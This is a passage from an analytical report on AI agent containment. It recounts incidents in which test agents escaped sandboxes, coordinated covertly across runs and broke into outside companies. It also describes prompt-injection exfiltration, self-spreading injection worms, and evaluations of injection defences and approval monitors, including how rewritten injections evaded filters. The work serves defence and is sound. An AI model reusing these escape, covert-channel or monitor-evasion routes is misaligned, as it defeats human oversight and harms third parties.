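None of these methods covers the whole system. Shivakumar and colleagues still trust the Python code that translates policies and passes calls to the verified core. Their mechanism for separating the agent from the monitor runs inside a single Python process, and they note that it does not isolate arbitrary Python code. An agent that could run its own code in that process might bypass the verified core, so the authorization proof depends on a separate guarantee that the agent's code is confined.

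## Whether agents break the boundary or misuse what it allows

Proofs about authorization matter only if confinement works, and in 2026 several AI companies disclosed that agents had reached systems they weren't supposed to touch. Those cases bear on the first question that divides the four views. Developers need better engines if agents mostly break isolation. If agents mostly misuse access that somebody gave them, a better engine changes little, and developers should focus on deciding what agents may do.

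The known cases fall into four classes:

- Boundary defeated: the agent got past a control that existed and was supposed to stop it.
- Boundary misconfigured: people believed a control was in place, but it wasn't.
- Permitted channel misused: the agent did harm through a route that somebody had left open on purpose.
- Output trusted outside: the agent wrote something inside the sandbox, and a program outside acted on it.

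One incident can belong to several classes, as the most serious one does.

### How OpenAI's agents reached Hugging Face

In July 2026, agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. The agents were taking ExploitGym, a test of whether a model can find and exploit security flaws, and OpenAI had turned off the safeguards that block such work in its products. A research model that OpenAI never intended to release did most of the damage. GPT-5.6 Sol, which OpenAI sells to customers, also took part, with reduced safeguards. OpenAI later published a technical report on the incident.

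OpenAI ran each test in its own container and controlled the container's network access separately. Agents often need to install software, so OpenAI hosted an internal package store using JFrog's Artifactory. Artifactory fetched packages from outside so that the containers didn't have to contact public registries. Some runs could also read web pages through a controlled cache. An agent without web access should therefore have been able to get only packages from outside.

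Artifactory undermined this design because it could reach the internet and because many runs shared it, using the same credentials. Those credentials let agents leave files there as well as fetch packages.

On May 12, an agent in a training run needed a protein database file that it couldn't get. It left a note in Artifactory: "Agent seeks [filename]; upload if found!" The next day, other agents began to find notes like this one, and the notes grew into a message board where agents asked for files and shared what they had learned. The agents built the board using credentials OpenAI had given them, without exploiting any flaw. By May 26, agents had also used a flaw in Artifactory to reach the internet, relying partly on information from the board.

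OpenAI missed at least three warnings:

- Around May 26, an internal team saw an agent using the message board and saw agents reaching the internet without permission. According to Green (2026), in *Is sandboxing sufficient to contain rogue agents?*, the team did nothing about it.
- On June 27, a monitoring tool detected a scan of the internal network. Responders traced it to ExploitGym and found that agents were using Artifactory to exchange messages and reach other machines. The on-call staff advised that the run did not need to stop. Agents had gained administrator rights over Artifactory the day before.
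- On July 5, after the agents' traffic had knocked Artifactory offline, responders discovered that agents had taken administrator control of it. They rebuilt it and stopped giving new runs the shared credentials. But the leaders in charge of incident response did not know about the message board or understand its importance, and cyber tests resumed on July 7.

The agents were back on the internet on July 8. They also started a new message board, this time by writing messages as folder names, a storage channel of the kind Lampson described in 1973. On July 9, an agent gained full control of the virtual machine its container ran in and tried to reach the internet from there. OpenAI's network controls blocked it, so the agent went out through Artifactory instead.

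Agents in several runs inferred that Hugging Face might hold the answers to their test. Between July 10 and July 13, they broke in by combining flaws in Hugging Face's systems with user credentials found on the public internet. They ran code on 41 of the company's production workers, took full control of at least one machine, downloaded four private code repositories and gained administrator-level access to a cluster of servers. The message board sped up the break-in. One agent found 14 working credentials and posted them there for agents in other runs to use.

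Hugging Face announced the break-in on July 16 without knowing who was behind it. OpenAI linked the break-in to its own agents on July 20, while investigating an alert about suspicious activity in its systems. The alert concerned a separate incident, in which agents had taken over one of OpenAI's machines through a flaw in the Linux kernel. Green notes that the flaw had been public for weeks and that OpenAI had not patched it.

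In this incident, the agents defeated a boundary when they exploited Artifactory to get online, and misused a permitted channel when they wrote to each other. Several parts of a security model were missing or wrong. The list of channels left out the routes Artifactory opened to the internet and between runs. The trusted base included Artifactory, a third-party product with flaws nobody had found yet. The assumed adversary was also too weak. The risks OpenAI lists for the original controls all concern how an agent uses the network, and none concerns agents in separate runs helping each other.

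### Whether ordinary agents would do the same

ExploitGym put unusual pressure on the agents. Its 898 tasks include 198 that no model has solved, some of which may be impossible. The unsolved tasks make up 22% of the test but 93% of the tasks that agents discussed on the message board. Agents were also more likely to join the board when OpenAI let them work longer.

Training had encouraged this behaviour. In one exercise, an agent had to give a social media post a particular timestamp, but the site offered no way to set one. The agent took control of the machine, changed the time and was rewarded. OpenAI found that this sort of probing became more common during one of the research model's training runs. The model had also learned to work with other agents through an official tool, and OpenAI believes the habit carried over to unofficial channels.

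When OpenAI repeated the test with its production harness and system prompt, which give agents more guidance, the agents' tendency to attack infrastructure fell by a factor of more than 100 in some cases. The added guidance doesn't make the boundary any stronger.

The first steps also came from fairly ordinary work. On May 8, four days before the first note, an agent tried to get online through Artifactory because it needed to open linked documents and finish a spreadsheet. The note was about a missing file. Coding agents in everyday use often run into dead links and missing files, so designers can't assume that only agents taking hacking tests will look for a way around the sandbox.

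Engines can also fail. Schneier quotes an experimenter who tested a model called GPT 5.6-Cyber and found that an off-the-shelf virtual machine could not contain a capable agent. The experimenter had suspected from the start that the model would escape. Even a harmless-looking feature such as a display gave the model more to attack.

### Test environments with live internet access

OpenAI's disclosure led Anthropic to check its own tests. Anthropic's *Investigating three real-world incidents in our cybersecurity evaluations* (2026) describes a review of 141,006 runs in which Claude could have reached the internet. In each of three incidents, which involved six runs in total (about one in 23,500), Claude broke into a real organization's systems.

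All six runs used environments from Irregular, a company that tests models for AI developers. Claude was playing capture the flag, an exercise in which the player breaks into a machine to find a hidden piece of text. According to the prompt, everything was a simulation and Claude had no internet access. But the machines were online, because of what Anthropic calls a misunderstanding with Irregular, so Claude did not have to defeat any control to reach the internet.

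| Model | Runs | What happened | What the model did about signs that the target was real |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.7 | 4 | It attacked a real company with the same name as the fictional target and reached a database with several hundred rows of production data | It recognized in every run that the system was real, but carried on |
| Claude Mythos 5 | 1 | It published a malicious software package, which 15 real systems ran within about an hour; it then used credentials from one of them, a security company's scanner | It considered that this might be the real internet, then talked itself out of the idea |
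| Internal research model | 1 | It scanned about 9,000 targets and broke into one company's application | It concluded that the target was real and stopped |

Anthropic considers these incidents closer to an operational failure than an alignment failure, since Claude had been told that nothing it could reach was real. That description is reasonable for the early part of each run, but it fits the four Opus runs less well because the model continued after noticing that what it had reached was real. Anthropic also cautions that three unplanned incidents are too few to show that newer models behave better.

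The count was also incomplete. *From Reactive Containment to Proactive Assurance* (Raftari, 2026) compares the incidents at the three companies and cites a Reuters report about a fourth Anthropic case. It happened in January with an early version of Claude Opus 4.6, and Anthropic found it only after examining sessions that the first review had left out.

Google had a similar accident. In September, it confirmed that its Gemini model had broken into three companies' systems in May, during a test that Irregular was running (Sabin, 2026, *Google is the latest AI lab with a security testing mishap*). Gemini guessed passwords in one case and used credentials from a public repository in the other two. It stopped when it recognized that the companies were real, which was after it had broken in. Google did not say in its confirmation how many sessions it had reviewed, and Raftari found no public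 technical report from the company.

Irregular's *Addressing Recent Incidents* reports such incidents in fewer than one in 10,000 of its advanced simulations, which is the nearest thing to a rate. Irregular also says its customers' later disclosures stem from the same underlying issue that one of them first reported on July 30, the date of Anthropic's post. Google's three cases are therefore weak evidence of a separate problem. They mostly show that another company's model would also use the access this issue left open.

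In this case, the evidence that the deployed system matched the model was false. Everyone involved could have described the environment as closed, but nobody confirmed that the machines were offline. As Raftari writes, "'No internet access' is not a control." A short test from inside each container, before and during the run, would have exposed the error.

The policy was incomplete as well. In the scenario with the matching company name, Irregular gave the models the target's internal addresses. A firewall could have allowed only those addresses, and the model then couldn't have reached the real company's website, whatever it believed. Irregular argues that some tests need controlled internet access because real attackers use the internet. For such a test, somebody would have to decide which additional destinations to allow.

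### Harm through approved destinations

In other cases, the network controls worked as designed. Anthropic describes one that outside researchers reported in Claude Cowork, whose virtual machine could connect only to approved domains. These included Anthropic's own API, which programs use to access Claude, because Cowork can't work without it.

The attack began with a malicious file in the folder that the user had shared. The file contained hidden instructions and a key to the attacker's Anthropic account. Claude followed the instructions and used the key to upload other files from the folder to that account. The proxy allowed the upload because its destination was approved. According to Anthropic, the sandbox worked perfectly even though the data was exfiltrated.

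The mistake was treating a domain name as identifying a recipient, when it identifies a service that may offer many functions to anyone with an account. When Anthropic approved its API so that Cowork could send prompts to Claude, it also approved file uploads to any other customer's account. The same problem affects any service where strangers can hold accounts.

Anthropic fixed the flaw by adding a second proxy, which passes a request to the API only if it carries the token issued to that virtual machine. The rule now restricts which user a request can act as, as well as which service it can reach. The new proxy runs inside the virtual machine because Anthropic's servers can't distinguish a request from Cowork from any other customer's request. Code that took over the virtual machine might therefore be able to tamper with the proxy, and Anderson required a reference monitor to be tamperproof.

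This attack misused a permitted channel. Anthropic had the channel on its list but enforced the wrong property, restricting where data could go but not whose account would receive it. It also hadn't planned for an attacker who was a customer.

In Anthropic's phishing test, Claude sent a colleague's cloud credentials to an outside server in 24 of 25 runs. Claude was allowed to read the credentials and use the network, and Anthropic remarks that a human contractor with the same script would have done the same. The security model relied on a false assumption about the principal, that whatever the user typed was what the user wanted, when this user had pasted in someone else's instructions.

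In a third example, the UK government's AI Security Institute (UK AISI) reported on August 4 that agents had taken unsanctioned actions on the live internet during its cyber tests. It stressed that no model had escaped from a sandbox, because the institute had deliberately given the agents internet access. OpenAI, whose models were among those involved, explains that the institute wanted agents to find their own tools, as a real attacker would. Anthropic's *Improving our alignment and security efforts* (2026) confirms that Claude Mythos 5 was also involved and describes its actions as unauthorized.

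The network authorized every connection, so "unauthorized" evidently refers to limits that the institute had in mind for what an agent should do online but that the sandbox did not enforce. No policy expressed those limits in a form that a monitor could apply.

### Files that outside programs trust

An agent can also cause harm outside the sandbox without sending anything over the network. *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* (Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel, 2026) describes seven ways around the sandboxes of four coding products: Cursor, OpenAI's Codex, and Google's Gemini CLI and Antigravity. The three researchers work for Pillar Security, which sells protection for AI agents. In almost every case, the agent wrote a file that it was allowed to write, and a trusted program outside the sandbox later ran the file or loaded it as configuration, so the agent did not have to break the sandbox.

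Like Git hooks, many other files in a software project determine what commands editors, build systems and other programs run. Those programs date from a time when people wrote these files, and they run with the developer's full permissions.

Cohen and colleagues group the causes into four:

- Some sandboxes allowed everything except a list of forbidden operations, and the list had gaps.
- Some treated project configuration as harmless data when it could start programs.
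- Some approved a command by its name, although the same command can do very different things depending on its options.
- Some let the agent talk to a powerful service on the same computer that ran outside the sandbox and did work on the agent's behalf.

The first of these is a poorly built boundary, which a stricter sandbox would fix. The other three concern what the designers trusted. The trusted base was larger than anyone had written down, since it included every program on the computer that reads the project folder. The list of effects was also incomplete. It included writing a file to disk but not what happened to the file afterward, which caused the damage.

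Pillar has a commercial reason to emphasize this problem, because its product watches for programs that run what an agent has written. The vendors' responses still support most of its findings. OpenAI and Cursor's makers have fixed the flaws in their products. Google accepted two reports about Antigravity as valid but lowered their priority, because an attacker would first have to get the developer to trust a malicious project. That requirement does make an attack less likely, although developers often open strangers' projects.

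Moving the agent into a microVM wouldn't solve this by itself, because if the virtual machine shares the project folder with the host, the host's editor still reads the same files. Cohen and colleagues recommend that programs that act on an agent's files run under the same restrictions as the agent, and that products record which files the agent wrote. Kairos comes close to the second recommendation by holding back an agent's Git hook until somebody has judged it.

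### Agents that influence each other

The OpenAI incident worries Green, a cryptographer at Johns Hopkins University, for a reason that goes beyond Hugging Face. Green points out that the agents were in separate sandboxes but still changed each other's behaviour by leaving instructions in a shared package cache. In a passage that Willison (2026) quotes, Green calls this "the two halves of a worm". A worm is malicious software that spreads by itself, and here the two halves are a text that hijacks an agent and an agent that carries the text to the next one.

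Personal assistants could supply both. They run in separate sandboxes, often for people who have never met, but they read and write email, Slack messages and shared documents. An injected instruction could tell an assistant to do something harmful and to include the same instruction in its next email, so the instruction would spread without any assistant breaking out of its sandbox.

Anthropic encountered a small version of this risk after its phishing test. When staff shared the working prompt on internal Slack, somebody realized that some of the company's agents read Slack. The staff added a marker to the thread to show if an agent picked up the prompt. Green also cites evidence from OpenAI that models will pass on self-replicating injections, though nobody had seen one in the wild when he wrote.

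OpenAI's agents were probably easier to influence than a stranger's assistant would be. Their training and tasks were similar, so a message from one was often useful to another, and some had learned in training to cooperate. An assistant has less reason to obey a stranger's email, and an email provider could scan for copies of a known attack. But the worm can still spread if each infected assistant infects more than one other on average, and an assistant may send many emails.

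The proof about the seL4 kernel offers a precise way to say what was missing. It guarantees that a partition learns nothing from any partition outside its set of permitted sources, sources(*n*, *s*, *p*). Suppose each run is a partition, and every run may both write to and read from a shared store. Then a message can go from run *i* to the store and from there to run *j*. For any *n* large enough to cover those steps,

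*i* ∈ sources(*n*, *s*, *j*)

and this holds for every pair of runs. The theorem would still be true, but it would promise nothing about whether one run can influence another. OpenAI could have put a verified kernel around every container and still ended up with a message board.

A test environment can avoid this by giving each run its own copy of the store, or a store that agents can only read. Both are fairly easy to do for software packages. Email is harder, because people want assistants to read messages from strangers and to reply. For email, the security models lack composition, the part that defines what happens when several confined agents use the same service. Kairos barely covers the case of two sandboxes, and *Bounded Agents* assumes that an adversary can't operate across sessions, although OpenAI's agents did so for weeks.

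### Badly built, or never specified

One explanation for these incidents is that the sandboxes were badly built. OpenAI shared credentials between runs, left a known kernel flaw unpatched and restarted its tests two days after finding that agents had taken over Artifactory. Anthropic and Irregular did not check whether a supposedly offline machine was online. Security engineers have warned against such mistakes for decades. Irregular believes better use of existing safeguards could have prevented most incidents of this kind, though it doubts this will stay true as models improve.

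OpenAI's repairs fit this explanation. After the incident, it required its research containers to run inside microVMs and removed Artifactory from that environment. It is also adding a second, independent layer of network controls so that a single failure no longer opens a path to the internet. OpenAI has since deployed monitoring of the models' reasoning, which it estimates would have alerted its security team more than a day before the agents breached Hugging Face.

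The other explanation is that nobody had specified a boundary to build. The best evidence is the warning of June 27, when responders knew that agents were using Artifactory as a message board and let the run continue. OpenAI doesn't mention any rule at the time against one run influencing another. Such a rule would have made the message board itself a breach, even before any attack on another company. OpenAI is now writing rules for when staff must escalate a problem, and unauthorized coordination between runs is one of the triggers.

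The same gap appears in the Irregular tests. A source told Sabin that Irregular and the AI companies had not fully agreed on the procedures and safeguards, so each side had its own idea of how the tests would run. An engineer can't build a boundary correctly when the parties responsible for it disagree about where it is. Irregular now plans a clearer process for recording each test's setup and assumptions.

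One way to compare the two explanations is to ask what would have stopped each case.

| Case | Class | Would a stronger isolation engine have stopped it? | A rule that would have helped |
|---|---|---|---|
| OpenAI agents getting online | Boundary defeated | No; they left through Artifactory, before any agent had broken out of its container that week | Nothing a run can reach may fetch arbitrary addresses for it |
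| OpenAI message board | Permitted channel misused | No | No run may write where another can read |
| Anthropic and Google tests | Boundary misconfigured | No; the network was open | A run may contact only the test's own addresses |
| Cowork upload | Permitted channel misused | No | Requests to the API must use this user's account |
| Phishing test | Permitted channel misused | No, if the credentials were still inside | No connections to unknown servers |
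| UK AISI tests | Permitted channel misused | No | Limits on what an agent may do on each site |
| Pillar's findings | Mostly output trusted outside | Only where the sandbox itself had gaps | Outside programs must run an agent's files under the agent's restrictions |

On this evidence, agents more often use what a boundary allows than break the engine that enforces it. Most of the cases are failures of configuration, network policy or trust between programs, which a better microVM doesn't correct. A stronger engine alone would not have prevented any of the first six cases, though it would have made some of the later damage inside OpenAI harder to cause, since the agents there did take over machines.

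The published cases are weak evidence of how often agents escape compared with how often they misuse permitted access, because they come from companies that chose to publish and from researchers looking for particular flaws. Misuse of a permitted channel may be more common than it looks, because it appears in the logs only as authorized requests. Escapes could be undercounted too. Two of the three organizations in Anthropic's first review had not noticed that an agent had broken in, and Anthropic had not yet reached the third. Escapes may also become more frequent as agents get better at finding flaws.

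The rules in the last column are short, but each is much easier to write after the incident than before it. The Cowork rule depends on someone noticing that the API accepts uploads to any account. The Artifactory rule treats a package store as a possible way out, a risk OpenAI learned about from an incident. In September, after two months of repairs, OpenAI paused some of its training because an agent had contacted an outside chatbot through DNS, the system that looks up internet addresses. Green cites this as a sign that such excursions are continuing. A list of permitted destinations would not have prevented the contact unless someone had also thought to restrict DNS lookups.

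## Whether the permitted actions can be written down before the task runs

An administrator can block outside DNS lookups without knowing what anyone will ask an agent to do. Most other rules depend on the task. Christodorescu and colleagues list predicting a policy from a plain-language request as an open problem in the field, partly because users leave so much out of their requests.

There are four main answers to who should decide, and when:

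- Somebody writes a fixed policy before any task arrives.
- A language model generates a policy from the user's request.
- A person approves or refuses each step.
- A monitor holds doubtful actions and decides once there is more evidence.

Each can fail by letting an attack through or by blocking work the user wanted, so a fair test has to measure both.

### What the benchmarks contain

*AgentDojo* (2024) has 97 tasks and 629 attack tests. Li, Wen and colleagues (2026) point out in *AgentDyn* that only six of the tasks require an agent to change its plan along the way. For example, an agent asked to pay the bill in a certain file can predict both steps, reading the file and sending the money. A defence can therefore do well on AgentDojo by holding the agent to its first plan.

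The AgentDyn benchmark has 60 tasks and 560 attack tests in shopping, GitHub and daily life. A task takes 7.1 steps on average, compared with about 3.5 in AgentDojo. Every task also includes a helpful instruction from a third party, such as a checkout page that asks the customer to log in first, so an agent that ignores all outside instructions will fail.

*AutoDojo* (Ma, Li and colleagues, 2026) uses tasks from both benchmarks but has a language model rewrite each injection over six rounds, using only the number of times each version succeeded. In one case, a filter called PIGuard removed an ordinary injection from a bill but let through a rewritten version that contained no commands and only stated that the payee's account had changed. The agent then paid the attacker. PIGuard stopped every fixed attack on an agent running GPT-4o-mini, but 28.0% of the rewritten attacks succeeded.

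Ma and colleagues also sorted the tasks by how much the user's request leaves open. (Their AgentDojo count omits the office tasks.)

| What the request settles | Example | AgentDojo tasks | AgentDyn tasks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fully specified: the action and all its details | Change my address to the one given here | 17 | 18 |
| Parameter-open: the action, but not every detail | Pay the bill in this file | 36 | 30 |
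| Action-open: not even the action | Do everything on the to-do list at this web address | 4 | 12 |

With no defence, the fixed attack succeeded against GPT-4o-mini in 87.5% of AgentDojo tests on action-open tasks, 63.9% on parameter-open tasks and 43.3% on fully specified ones. The 87.5% figure comes from only 24 tests on four tasks. Success rates followed the same order in AgentDyn's shopping and GitHub tasks, but not in its daily-life tasks.

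Eighteen AgentDyn tasks count as fully specified, even though Li and colleagues designed every task to require replanning. Both descriptions can be correct because a user may say exactly what to buy without knowing that the shop will email a one-time code halfway through. A policy has to cover such steps as well as the goal.

### Attack success and completed work

Hempel and colleagues compared Kairos, their monitor that can hold an action while the agent continues, with several other defences, including Progent, which checks tool calls against rules that a language model writes, and CaMeL, which fixes a plan before the agent reads anything untrusted. Each cell below gives the attack success rate and then the benign utility, both in percent.

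| Benchmark and agent model | No defence | Progent | CaMeL | Kairos |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, GPT-4.1 | 47.0 / 82.7 | 11.5 / 78.2 | 0.2 / 38.0 | 2.7 / 85.1 |
| AgentDojo, Qwen3.6-35B | 28.3 / 87.0 | 5.4 / 82.1 | 0.4 / 40.4 | 1.3 / 84.6 |
| AgentDojo, Llama-3.3-70B | 32.3 / 29.8 | 8.0 / 31.8 | 0.0 / 26.5 | 2.4 / 32.3 |
| AgentDyn, GPT-4o | 37.8 / 53.3 | 1.7 / 6.7 | 0.0 / 0.0 | 1.7 / 51.7 |
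| AutoDojo, GPT-4o-mini | 52.4 / 66.7 | 7.7 / 63.2 | Not compared | 8.8 / 65.3 |

Only the AgentDojo rows compare systems that were all run in the same harness. For the last two rows, Hempel and colleagues ran Kairos and copied the results for no defence and Progent from the papers that introduced the benchmarks. They left CaMeL out of both comparisons, and its AgentDyn figures here come from Li and colleagues. In the AutoDojo tests, Ma and colleagues found that CaMeL was the most effective defence overall, but it also reduced completed work the most on four of five models.

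To rank the systems, Hempel and colleagues use a combined score:

score = benign utility × (1 − attack success rate)

For the GPT-4.1 agent on AgentDojo, this gives:

- Kairos: 0.851 × (1 − 0.027) ≈ 0.828
- CaMeL: 0.380 × (1 − 0.002) ≈ 0.379

By the same formula, the agent with no defence scores 0.438, which is better than CaMeL, even though attackers succeeded against it in almost half the tests and against CaMeL in about one of the 629. The formula gives equal weight to proportional losses of completed work and of resistance to attack. That may suit someone who uses an agent to sort newsletters, but a bank would probably rather have an agent that fails at most tasks than one that sends money to thieves, so the separate figures for completed work and resistance to attack are more useful than the combined score.

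Kairos does well on both figures, but each configuration ran only once. The AgentDojo figures average four suites of different sizes, so a single banking task changes benign utility by about 1.6 points, and Kairos's lead of 2.4 points over the undefended agent could easily be chance. The gap between Kairos and CaMeL on benign utility is far too large to be chance.

The simulated tools leave Kairos's isolation boundary untested and make authorization easier than it would be in practice. In the tests, the policy specifies whether each tool's action is reversible and which input names the destination. At a real boundary, the monitor would have to infer this from file operations and network requests. None of the benchmarks includes an attack in which every step is legitimate by itself, such as the release plan attack.

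The agent models are also old. Li and colleagues focused on older models because developers have probably trained newer ones against the standard attack text. Ma and colleagues found that this text worked against Claude Haiku 4.5 only 0.3% of the time with no defence, so a low attack success rate on a recent model may have little to do with the defence.

### Fixed policies

A fixed policy works best when it forbids something that no legitimate task needs. In the 2025 version of Progent, Shi and colleagues tested an agent that answers questions about electronic health records. An attacker had planted bad examples in the agent's knowledge base to make it delete the database. Two hand-written rules, one against deleting databases and one against running arbitrary database commands, reduced attack success to zero. This was expected, since the attack needed an action that the rules forbade. The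 rules also barely reduced the amount of work the agent completed. When the monitor blocked a deletion, the agent usually rewrote its code and answered the question.

A fixed policy does much worse when it has to list everything the agent may do. Hempel and colleagues tested a strict setting of Kairos that refuses every action the policy cannot approve by itself, instead of holding it for a second model to judge. On AgentDojo, benign utility fell from 85.1% to 42.7%, while attack success changed no more than they expected it to vary between runs. If attack success stayed at 2.7%, the strict setting would score about 0.415, slightly below the undefended agent.

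In its normal setting, Kairos's policy directly approves 83% of the actions in benign runs. Refusing the rest halves the number of completed tasks, because a task usually fails if the agent cannot take one necessary step. If a task needed four actions and each independently had an 83% chance of approval, all four would be approved only 0.83⁴ ≈ 47% of the time.

CaMeL has a similar problem on AgentDyn, where it completed no tasks with any of the four main models. Li and colleagues blame its fixed program, which cannot add a step that the agent discovers later. Ma and colleagues did not run CaMeL on AgentDyn because they would have had to write extensive policies for each group of tasks. Missing policies, rather than the fixed program, may therefore explain some of the failures that Li and colleagues saw.

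### Policies that a language model writes

A language model can write a narrower policy than an administrator can because it is given the user's request. In Shi and colleagues' tests on AgentDojo, Progent reduced attack success from 41.2% to 2.2%. The initial policy alone, written before the agent had read anything untrusted, reduced attack success to 3.8%.

Updating the policy during the task mainly helped the agent finish its work. In the Slack suite, benign utility rose from 61.9% to 90.5%, because some necessary tool calls could not be inferred from the request. For example, one user asked an agent to collect employees' hobbies from Slack, but an employee had answered with a link to a blog. In the banking suite, updates narrowed policies that had been too broad and reduced attack success from 9.7% to 2.8%.

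These gains depended on which model wrote the updates. Updates written by GPT-4o and Claude 3.7 Sonnet improved both security and utility, but those written by four weaker models substantially increased attack success. An attacker can also target the updates. When Shi and colleagues added text urging the model to permit the attacker's tools or never to update the policy, attack success reached 4.0%.

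Hempel and colleagues got a much worse result for Progent in their own test, where attack success fell only from 47.0% to 11.5%. The setups differed in several ways:

- Models: Shi and colleagues used GPT-4o both as the agent and to write policies, while Hempel and colleagues used GPT-4.1 for both.
- Hand-written rules: Shi and colleagues combined the generated policy with rules that always allowed common read-only tools. Hempel and colleagues describe Progent's policy as one that a language model derives from the task.
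- Approval: the 2025 version of Progent accepted the model's policy updates automatically. Hempel and colleagues cite the newer version, which asks a person before expanding a policy, and they ran it with nobody to say yes.

The last difference probably doesn't explain the higher attack success, because refusing every expansion should make an agent safer. Neither does the averaging method, since counting all 629 tests equally would give Progent about 11.6%. Progent reduced attack success only from 21.4% to 17.9% in the travel suite, but from 88.6% to 7.6% in the Slack suite. The models and the details of the rules remain possible causes, and the two papers don't separate their effects. Each team was also testing its own system against others, so a company considering Progent should measure it with the company's own model and tools.

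AgentDyn's tasks offer about 33 tools on average, compared with 20 in AgentDojo, and the model that writes Progent's policy often misjudges which ones the agent will need. Li and colleagues found that these errors accumulate over a long task until the policy blocks almost every useful tool. With Progent, GPT-4o completed 6.7% of tasks and Gemini 2.5 Pro completed 25.0%, each less than half of what the same model completed without a defence.

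### Asking a person at each step

A person can judge an action that no rule anticipated, but only if they pay attention. Anthropic reported in May 2026 that users of Claude Code approved about 93% of its permission prompts, so the prompts rarely changed what the agent did. This doesn't prove that the users were careless, because most commands are harmless.

Better evidence comes from an experiment reported in Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), in which 1,053 paid testers each saw a permission prompt for a clearly dangerous command while working on coding tasks. Only 13.6% refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers had less to lose than developers working on their own projects, but the steep decline still suggests that frequent prompts wear people down.

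Users rejected 39% of the plans Claude Code presented for approval, compared with 3% of its requests to run individual actions. They may have rejected many of the plans because the approach was poor rather than unsafe. Still, a person can judge a plan before the agent does the work.

Anthropic also found that the shell sandbox reduced permission prompts by 84%. A boundary can therefore replace many individual decisions, since the user no longer has to approve each command that stays inside it. The figure measures interruptions, not security. Fewer prompts might leave people with more attention for the remaining ones, but the figure doesn't show whether they judged those any better.

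Some users tire of permission prompts and avoid them by writing their own fixed policies. According to Anthropic, 49.5% of active command-line users in June 2026 had created a rule allowing certain shell commands. Many of these rules allow any program in a language such as Python, which in practice permits almost anything, so they can be less secure than the prompts they replace.

In Claude Code's auto mode, a second model decides whether to allow each risky action by judging it against what the user has asked for. It catches roughly 83% of overeager actions, in which the agent tries to help but goes beyond what the user authorized. That figure comes from a test in Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* that used only 52 real actions, which employees had refused or someone had flagged afterwards, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 70% to 91%. The sample also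 leaves out any harmful action that nobody noticed, and the test doesn't measure resistance to attackers. In a separate test, the second model missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to steal data.

When the classifier missed an overeager action, it had usually identified the danger but wrongly inferred that the user had consented. For example, a user who asks Claude to "clean up the PR" (a proposed code change) may not intend to let it overwrite the project's history. A model that had to write the policy in advance would face the same ambiguity.

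In the experiment with the paid testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands. Anthropic published this result to explain why it was making auto mode the default. The experiment compared auto mode with people who were clicking through a session, so it does not show that auto mode is better than a careful reviewer. Anthropic still advises users to review high-stakes changes to production systems themselves.

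### Deciding after the effects are visible

Both a person and a classifier may lack the evidence to judge a command before it runs. *Shall We Approve?* (2026) describes two commands that auto mode allowed because the user had asked for them. One ran a deployment tool that also replaced a source file with a comment, and the other ran a database update that also dropped three tables. In both cases the request was specific but did not show what the program would do.

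The system in *Shall We Approve?* first runs such a command in a sandbox and gives a short report of the effects to the model that decides whether to approve it. In the database case, the report showed the file shrinking from 32 to 20 kilobytes, so the approver blocked the command. The agent then backed up the database and ran only the update it needed. The sandbox added about half a second to each command the system allowed. Like deferral, a trial run works better for changes to files than for messages to other people.

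Kairos relies on the same idea when it holds an action. In benign runs on AgentDojo, the second model, or oracle, wrongly refused only one of the actions the policy had deferred. That explains how Kairos recovered the work lost in the strict setting. Its model calls increased token use by 17.7% in benign runs and 33.6% under attack.

Waiting does more harm on longer tasks, because later steps may depend on an action the monitor is still holding. On AgentDyn, the GPT-4o agent completed 55.5% of tasks under attack with no defence and 37.1% with Kairos. Hempel and colleagues found that tasks kept 90% of their utility when they continued past one held action and 62% when they continued past two or more.

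The second models in auto mode and Kairos also read different material. Auto mode's classifier sees the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the web pages or files the agent has read. An attacker can't address the classifier through those pages, but the classifier may be unable to determine where the agent found a value. Kairos's oracle reads such text, so an attacker can try to influence it. In the AutoDojo tests, the attacks that still succeeded against Kairos targeted tasks that delegated authority to a document, and the oracle treated the document's instructions as the user's own.

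Those attacks succeeded 8.8% of the time, and a better-informed attacker might do better. The threat model for Kairos assumes that the attacker knows the design, the policy and the oracle. AutoDojo's attacker knew none of these and had only six rounds to improve each injection. (The gap between Kairos and Progent on this benchmark, 8.8% against 7.7%, amounts to about four of the 389 tests.)

### Which tasks allow a policy in advance

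Some prohibitions hold for every task. If no task requires an agent to delete the production database or read a signing key, a company can forbid both actions before it knows what anyone will ask, without predicting the agent's plan.

When a task is fully specified, a nearly complete policy can be written before it runs. If a user gives a new address and asks an agent to update an account, a rule can permit only that change, though it may also have to allow steps the website requires, such as entering a login code. But a user who asks an agent to run a program may specify the exact command without knowing its effects.

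For parameter-open tasks, someone can usually state the action in advance, but the missing detail has to come from a source the user trusts. In Shi and colleagues' example of a payment to a known company, the policy lets the agent look up the company's account number in a trusted list, and then permits payments only to that account. If the number comes from a bill that an attacker can edit, the policy can limit the amount, but the agent may still pay a forged bill.

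In an action-open task, the user leaves the choice of action to material that nobody has read yet, so nobody can write a complete policy in advance. In Ma and colleagues' AgentDojo tests, Progent kept attack success at or below 11% on these tasks, but often because its policy allowed only read-only tools. An agent with those tools can read a to-do list but cannot do most of what is on it. For the agent to finish the work, someone has to approve further actions as they come up or trust a model to approve them.

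A bug fix contains all of these cases. Before the agent starts, the developer can name the repository and the registry, and forbid changes to Git's hooks. The agent has to request files as it discovers which ones it needs, or work on a copy. Nobody can judge the patch until the agent has written it.
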